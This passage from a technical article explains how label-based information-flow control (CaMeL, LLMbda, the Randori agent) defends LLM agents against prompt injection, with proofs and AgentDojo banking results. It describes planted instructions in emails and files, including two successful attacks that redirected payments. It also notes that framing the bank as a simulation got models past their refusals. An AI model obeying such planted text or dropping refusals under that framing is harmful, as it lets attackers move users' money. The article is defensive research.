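If the secret is true, the program skips the assignment in line 4, so `b` keeps its public label. If the secret is false, the program skips the assignment in line 3, so `a` keeps its public label and the tracker does not treat line 4 as depending on the secret. In both cases the tracker allows the last line, which publishes the opposite of the secret.

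Austin and Flanagan, in *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*, call a variable like `a` partially leaked. Its value depends on the secret in every run, but its label shows this in only some runs. An established remedy stops the program at line 3, because it is about to change a public variable inside a branch that depends on the secret. This also stops harmless programs, such as one that changes `a` and never publishes anything.

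### Retries outside the tracker

A dependency can also go untracked in the software around the interpreter. When a CaMeL program fails partway, the software sends the planner model an error message and asks for a new program. The error may depend on an email that the failed program read, and the new program depends on the error. But the retry loop runs outside the label tracker, so each attempt starts with a clean label.

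CaMeL censors the error messages to reduce this risk, but without a formal guarantee. Even an empty message reveals to the planner that something went wrong, and an attacker may be able to cause the failure. The argument that CaMeL's program depends only on the user's request and the tool descriptions therefore holds fully only for the first attempt. A retry can also repeat an action, such as a payment that the first program made before it crashed.

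### A language with conversations built in

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal programming language built around functions. Its main additions control the conversation with the model and the labels on data. A label is a set that can contain U for untrusted and S for secret, so data labeled with the empty set is trusted and public.

| Expression | What it does |
|---|---|
| `@e` | sends `e` to the model, adds the prompt and the reply to the conversation, and converts the reply into a value |
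| `fork e` | runs `e`, then restores the conversation to its earlier state |
| `clear` | empties the conversation |
| `{U}: e` | adds the label "untrusted" to `e` |
| `{S} ? e` | tests whether the label of `e` contains nothing except possibly S, which means that `e` is trusted |
| `assert {S} e` | stops the run if that test fails |

A developer can build Willison's quarantined model from three of these operations. In simplified form:

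```
quarantine = λprompt. fork (let _ = clear in @prompt)
```

The quarantined model receives the prompt in an empty conversation. `fork` then restores the main conversation, so the text the quarantined model read never enters it. This separation is built into CaMeL, but an LLMbda developer can change it or leave it out, and the interpreter tracks labels either way.

The model's reply can be a function, which the program can then run. The function takes the label of the conversation that produced it. If that conversation included a stranger's email, the code is untrusted, and so is everything it computes. The interpreter keeps a label $pc$ for the decisions that led to the current step, much as SPA does. When it runs a function with the label $m$, it uses

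$$pc' = pc \sqcup m$$

for the function's body. Conditionals work the same way, because the language builds them out of functions.

### An update that the interpreter refuses

In an agent, the conversation itself can act as the variable that leaks. Garby and colleagues give this example, in which the model is supposed to remember a value:

```
1  let secret = true in
2  let _ = @"Remember this value: x = false" in
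3  let _ = if {S}:secret then @"Set x = true" else () in
4  @"Give me the value of x"
```

| Line | $pc$ | Conversation's label | What happens |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | {} | {} | the model receives the value false |
| 3 | {S} | {} | the interpreter refuses the prompt |
| 4 | – | – | never runs |

A prompt may run only if $pc \sqsubseteq \ell$, where $\ell$ is the conversation's current label. On line 3, $pc$ contains S but $\ell$ doesn't, so the interpreter stops with an error before sending anything.

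If it had instead sent the prompt and relabelled the conversation as secret, that would protect the answer only when the secret is true. When the secret is false, line 3 sends nothing, the conversation stays public, and line 4 returns a public "false". A developer who needs this program can make the conversation secret before the branch, for example by sending a prompt labelled S, so that the final answer is secret in both cases.

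The refusal still leaves a smaller leak. The original program stops with an error if the secret is true and finishes if it is false, so anyone who can see whether it finished learns the secret. Askarov, Hunt and colleagues, in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit*, describe such leaks as the downside of a fairly permissive rule, which allows loops whose length depends on a secret. The leak can exceed one bit when a program produces output as it runs. A program could print 1, 2, 3 and so on, and hang when it reaches a secret number. This is a brute-force search, so it works for a four-digit PIN but would take far too long for a long random key.

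### What noninterference requires

If a program runs twice and only its secrets differ, noninterference requires everything labelled public to come out the same in both runs. The matching requirement for integrity is that everything labelled trusted must stay the same if only the untrusted data changes. LLMbda's version applies only when both runs finish.

To state this for all labels at once, write $e_0 \sim_m e_1$ if two programs, including their data, agree on everything that an observer at level $m$ may see. The requirement is then

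$$e_0 \sim_m e_1 \;\Rightarrow\; \text{result}(e_0) \sim_m \text{result}(e_1)$$

This property covers the program's decisions as well as the data it copies, whereas explicit secrecy, the property proved for FIDES, covers only the copied data. In LLMbda, the difference comes from one rule, which makes the interpreter use $pc \sqcup m$ when it runs a function. If the interpreter kept $pc$ unchanged, it would not track leaks through decisions. Garby and colleagues consider those leaks too serious to ignore in agents, where data can turn into code and an attacker can make such leaks efficient.

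They demonstrate the integrity half with an agent that should email a meeting reminder. The last message contains a planted instruction to send a cancellation instead. An ordinary agent with a single conversation sends the cancellation. In the protected version, the planner model writes a program before it sees the message, and the email tool asserts that the subject and body are trusted. Noninterference then guarantees that the planted text can't change the subject or body of any email that passes this check.

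The recipient has no such protection, because that example's policy doesn't check it.

### When the model answers at random

The February version of the theory assumed that a model always gives the same reply to the same conversation. Real models sample their replies at random, so changing a secret could change the probabilities of the results rather than a single result. A later version of the paper covers this case.

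Suppose a program can publish "yes" or "no", and sometimes stops without publishing anything:

| Result | Probability with secret A | Probability with secret B | Larger of the two |
|---|---|---|---|
| "yes" | 0.5 | 0.3 | 0.5 |
| "no" | 0.2 | 0.4 | 0.4 |
| Total for finished runs | 0.7 | 0.7 | 0.9 |

Let $\mu_0$ and $\mu_1$ be the probabilities in the two middle columns. They are compatible if some third list of probabilities $\omega$ is at least as large for every result and doesn't add up to more than 1:

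$$\mu_0 \le \omega, \qquad \mu_1 \le \omega, \qquad \sum_r \omega(r) \le 1$$

The last column of the table meets these conditions. Both secrets could therefore belong to a program that tends towards "yes" with probability 0.5 and "no" with probability 0.4 whatever the secret is, and in which the secret only determines which runs stop early.

Now suppose every run finishes, and the probability of "yes" is 0.7 for secret A and 0.5 for secret B. The larger probabilities are 0.7 for "yes" and 0.5 for "no". They add up to 1.2, which is more than 1, so the two lists are incompatible. Here the secret has changed the answer itself. If every run finishes, two lists are compatible only when their probabilities are identical.

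The main theorem is that any two programs that look alike to an observer produce compatible probabilities for what that observer sees. It holds for every label and every LLMbda program that doesn't use endorsement, including programs that run code written by a model.

Compatibility also limits how much a secret can affect the results. If $d_0$ and $d_1$ are the probabilities that the program doesn't finish, then

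$$\frac{1}{2}\sum_r |\mu_0(r) - \mu_1(r)| \;\le\; \frac{d_0 + d_1}{2}$$

In the table, the left side is 0.2 and the right side is 0.3. If a program fails in at most 1% of runs whatever the secret is, changing the secret can change the probability of any result by at most one percentage point. The limit is much looser for an agent that often stops with an error.

### How the proof works

It is hard to compare two random runs directly, because different replies can send them in different directions. Garby and colleagues instead define an imaginary way of running the program that never uses anything the observer may not see. It runs normally until a label rises above the observer's level, skips that part and puts an empty value in its place. They then prove three facts about it:

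- Skipping never makes a visible result less likely, because the program can't get stuck in a part it skips.
- The probabilities are the same for both secrets.
- The probabilities add up to at most 1.

If $\omega_0$ and $\omega_1$ are the probabilities with skipping, this gives

$$\mu_0 \le \omega_0 = \omega_1 \ge \mu_1$$

The shared value in the middle is the $\omega$ that compatibility requires.

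An older proof for a simpler language removes the secret parts from the program's text in advance. That isn't possible when a model writes some of the code during the run, so the secret parts have to be skipped as the program runs. Defining this skipping takes 76 rules, and the Lean file that proves the first fact is more than 12,000 lines long, which people would struggle to check by hand.

### Endorsing data without exposing secrets

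Strict noninterference would prevent some useful work. Suppose an agent sorts incoming email and puts the category in the subject line of its reply. The category comes from an untrusted email, so an email tool that requires a trusted subject would refuse it. LLMbda's `endorse` operation can relabel the category as trusted:

```
endorse {} ({U}: 42)            gives   {}: 42
endorse {} ({S}: "password")    gives   {S}: "password"

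the same operation inside an untrusted branch:
endorse {} ({U}: 42)            gives   {U}: 42
```

Endorsement can remove U but never S. It also can't make a value more trusted than the code that calls `endorse`. If a model writes code after reading an attacker's text, that code is untrusted, so any `endorse` in it has no effect.

This protection fails if an earlier endorsement has relabelled the attacker's text as trusted, because code based on that text then counts as trusted too. Garby and colleagues describe a stricter version that marks every endorsed value and blocks any further endorsement of it. This version also prevents generated code from using the unrestricted operation.

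The developer can limit endorsement to a fixed list of values, but the order of the steps matters:

```
if category in tags then endorse {} category          has no effect

let c = endorse {} category in                        works
if c in tags then c else category
```

In the first version, the condition reads the untrusted category, which makes the whole branch untrusted. The second version endorses a copy first and uses that copy only if it is on the list. Any other value keeps its original label. With eight tags, an attacker should be able to influence at most three bits, as with typed answers in FIDES, though nobody has yet proved this limit for LLMbda.

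The second theorem, which Garby and colleagues call insulated noninterference, covers programs that use `endorse`. Secrets can affect public results only through whether the program finishes, no matter what the attacker writes or the program endorses. The rule for `endorse` needed care because clearing the whole label would have made the password public. The theorem does not protect the integrity of endorsed data.

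### What Lean checks and what it assumes

The first LLMbda interpreter was about 4,000 lines of Python, separate from the proofs. The current interpreter is a Lean function, and the theorems are about that function. A third theorem shows that the interpreter's results have the probabilities used in the noninterference proof. ELBA and the system by Odersky and colleagues rely on established compilers instead, but neither has a machine-checked theorem about the complete agent.

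The proofs do not cover the whole system. The theory assumes that a model's replies follow fixed probabilities, given the conversation so far, and that each call is independent of the others. A service that carried memories from one conversation to the next would break that assumption. The network code that contacts the model is unverified, and the proofs treat it as an unknown function that returns text. The proofs also depend on Lean's own software working correctly, and they do not cover timing leaks.

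Like ELBA's proof, the theorems don't cover what the company hosting the model learns from the prompts.

As with the other systems that use labels, developers must get the labels and policies right. LLMbda's tools are functions that read and change a record representing the outside world. Garby and colleagues acknowledge that a better theory would include real external tools. In their tests, a layer of Python code copied AgentDojo's data into the program and copied the changes back.

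### Randori practises on artificial data

To test the language, they wrote an agent called Randori, after a form of free practice in Japanese martial arts. It works like this:

```
1  the planner model writes a program for the task
2  the program runs on artificial data
3  if it fails, the planner sees the error and tries again
4  once a program works, or the retries run out, the planner writes a final version
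5  the final version runs on the real data
```

During practice, every file contains the same placeholder text, and payments have no effect. No attacker has influenced this placeholder data, so the planner can read the error messages without becoming untrusted. The whole loop runs inside LLMbda, so LLMbda's labels cover the retries too. Because the agent doesn't retry on real data, a crash can't lead it to repeat a payment.

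Practice on artificial data doesn't test the final program, because the planner writes that program afresh, and nothing else tests it before it runs. Practice also doesn't reveal label errors, so a program can work on the artificial data and then fail a policy check on the real account.

Randori implements only part of CaMeL's banking policy. A transfer requires a trusted recipient, and a new password must be trusted. The rule for scheduling a new payment requires a trusted amount but, as listed in the paper, not a trusted recipient. An account number from an attacker's file could therefore pass that rule without endorsement, and the proof can't detect such a gap in the policy.

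The planner may also include `endorse` in its program. To pay a bill from a file, the program can ask a quarantined model for the account number, endorse the answer and send the money. The planner decides to endorse the answer before it sees the real file, so text in the file can't influence that decision. But the planner is itself a model, and it still decides which untrusted values to trust.

### Results on the banking suite

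Garby and colleagues ran Randori on the same banking tasks and attacks as CaMeL, again three times each, and divided the attacks into the same two groups.

| Model | Endorsement | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Resisted, extra call needed | Resisted, planned calls could be enough |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | allowed | 36 of 48 (75.0%) | 281 of 432 (65.0%) | 291 of 291 | 139 of 141 |
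| Qwen3.7-plus | allowed | 36 of 48 (75.0%) | 274 of 432 (63.4%) | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | allowed | 31 of 48 (64.6%) | 257 of 432 (59.5%) | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |
| Qwen3.7-plus | not allowed | 30 of 48 (62.5%) | 260 of 432 (60.2%) | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | not allowed | 26 of 48 (54.2%) | 243 of 432 (56.2%) | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |

With endorsement allowed, Randori resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. On GPT-5.2 it completed twice as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policies on. Endorsement explains only part of that lead. Without it, Randori still completed more tasks than CaMeL on MiMo-v2.5, probably in part because Randori's policies are less strict. The margins of error are wide, around 20 percentage points for tasks without attacks.

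The agent also had disadvantages. No model had been trained on LLMbda code, so the prompt had to include the language's grammar and 14 rules about common mistakes. The prompt also had to specify that the bank was a simulation, because models often refused to write code that sent money or changed passwords. The language can't yet recover from many ordinary errors, so a missing field in a record can end the task.

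As in the CaMeL tests, planning before reading the data should defeat most of these attacks even without the labels, so the attack results are limited evidence that the labels work. The proof gives much better reason to trust the label tracking.

### Why two attacks still succeeded

Both successful attacks occurred in runs of the same pair with GPT-5.2. The user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The agent endorsed the details from the file and paid the attacker.

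The interpreter correctly followed a program in which the planner had marked the file as trusted. This violated no theorem, because the main theorem doesn't cover programs that endorse data, and insulated noninterference protects only secrets. CaMeL's designers found the same case in their tests and did not count it among the attacks their system is meant to stop.

The stricter forms of endorsement wouldn't have helped much. The program endorsed the account number only once, so a ban on endorsing it again would have made no difference. A fixed list of permitted values works for categories but not for account numbers that the user hasn't supplied.

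Without endorsement, the policy would block this attack, because the recipient would still be untrusted. The experiment doesn't demonstrate this directly, since Garby and colleagues tested that setting only with the two models that had resisted every attack anyway. Disabling endorsement would likely make the agent less useful, since in that setting it completed six fewer attack-free runs with Qwen3.7-plus and five fewer with MiMo-v2.5. Three of the 16 tasks require the agent to act on a file's contents, and without endorsement Randori's policies block them, much as CaMeL's do.
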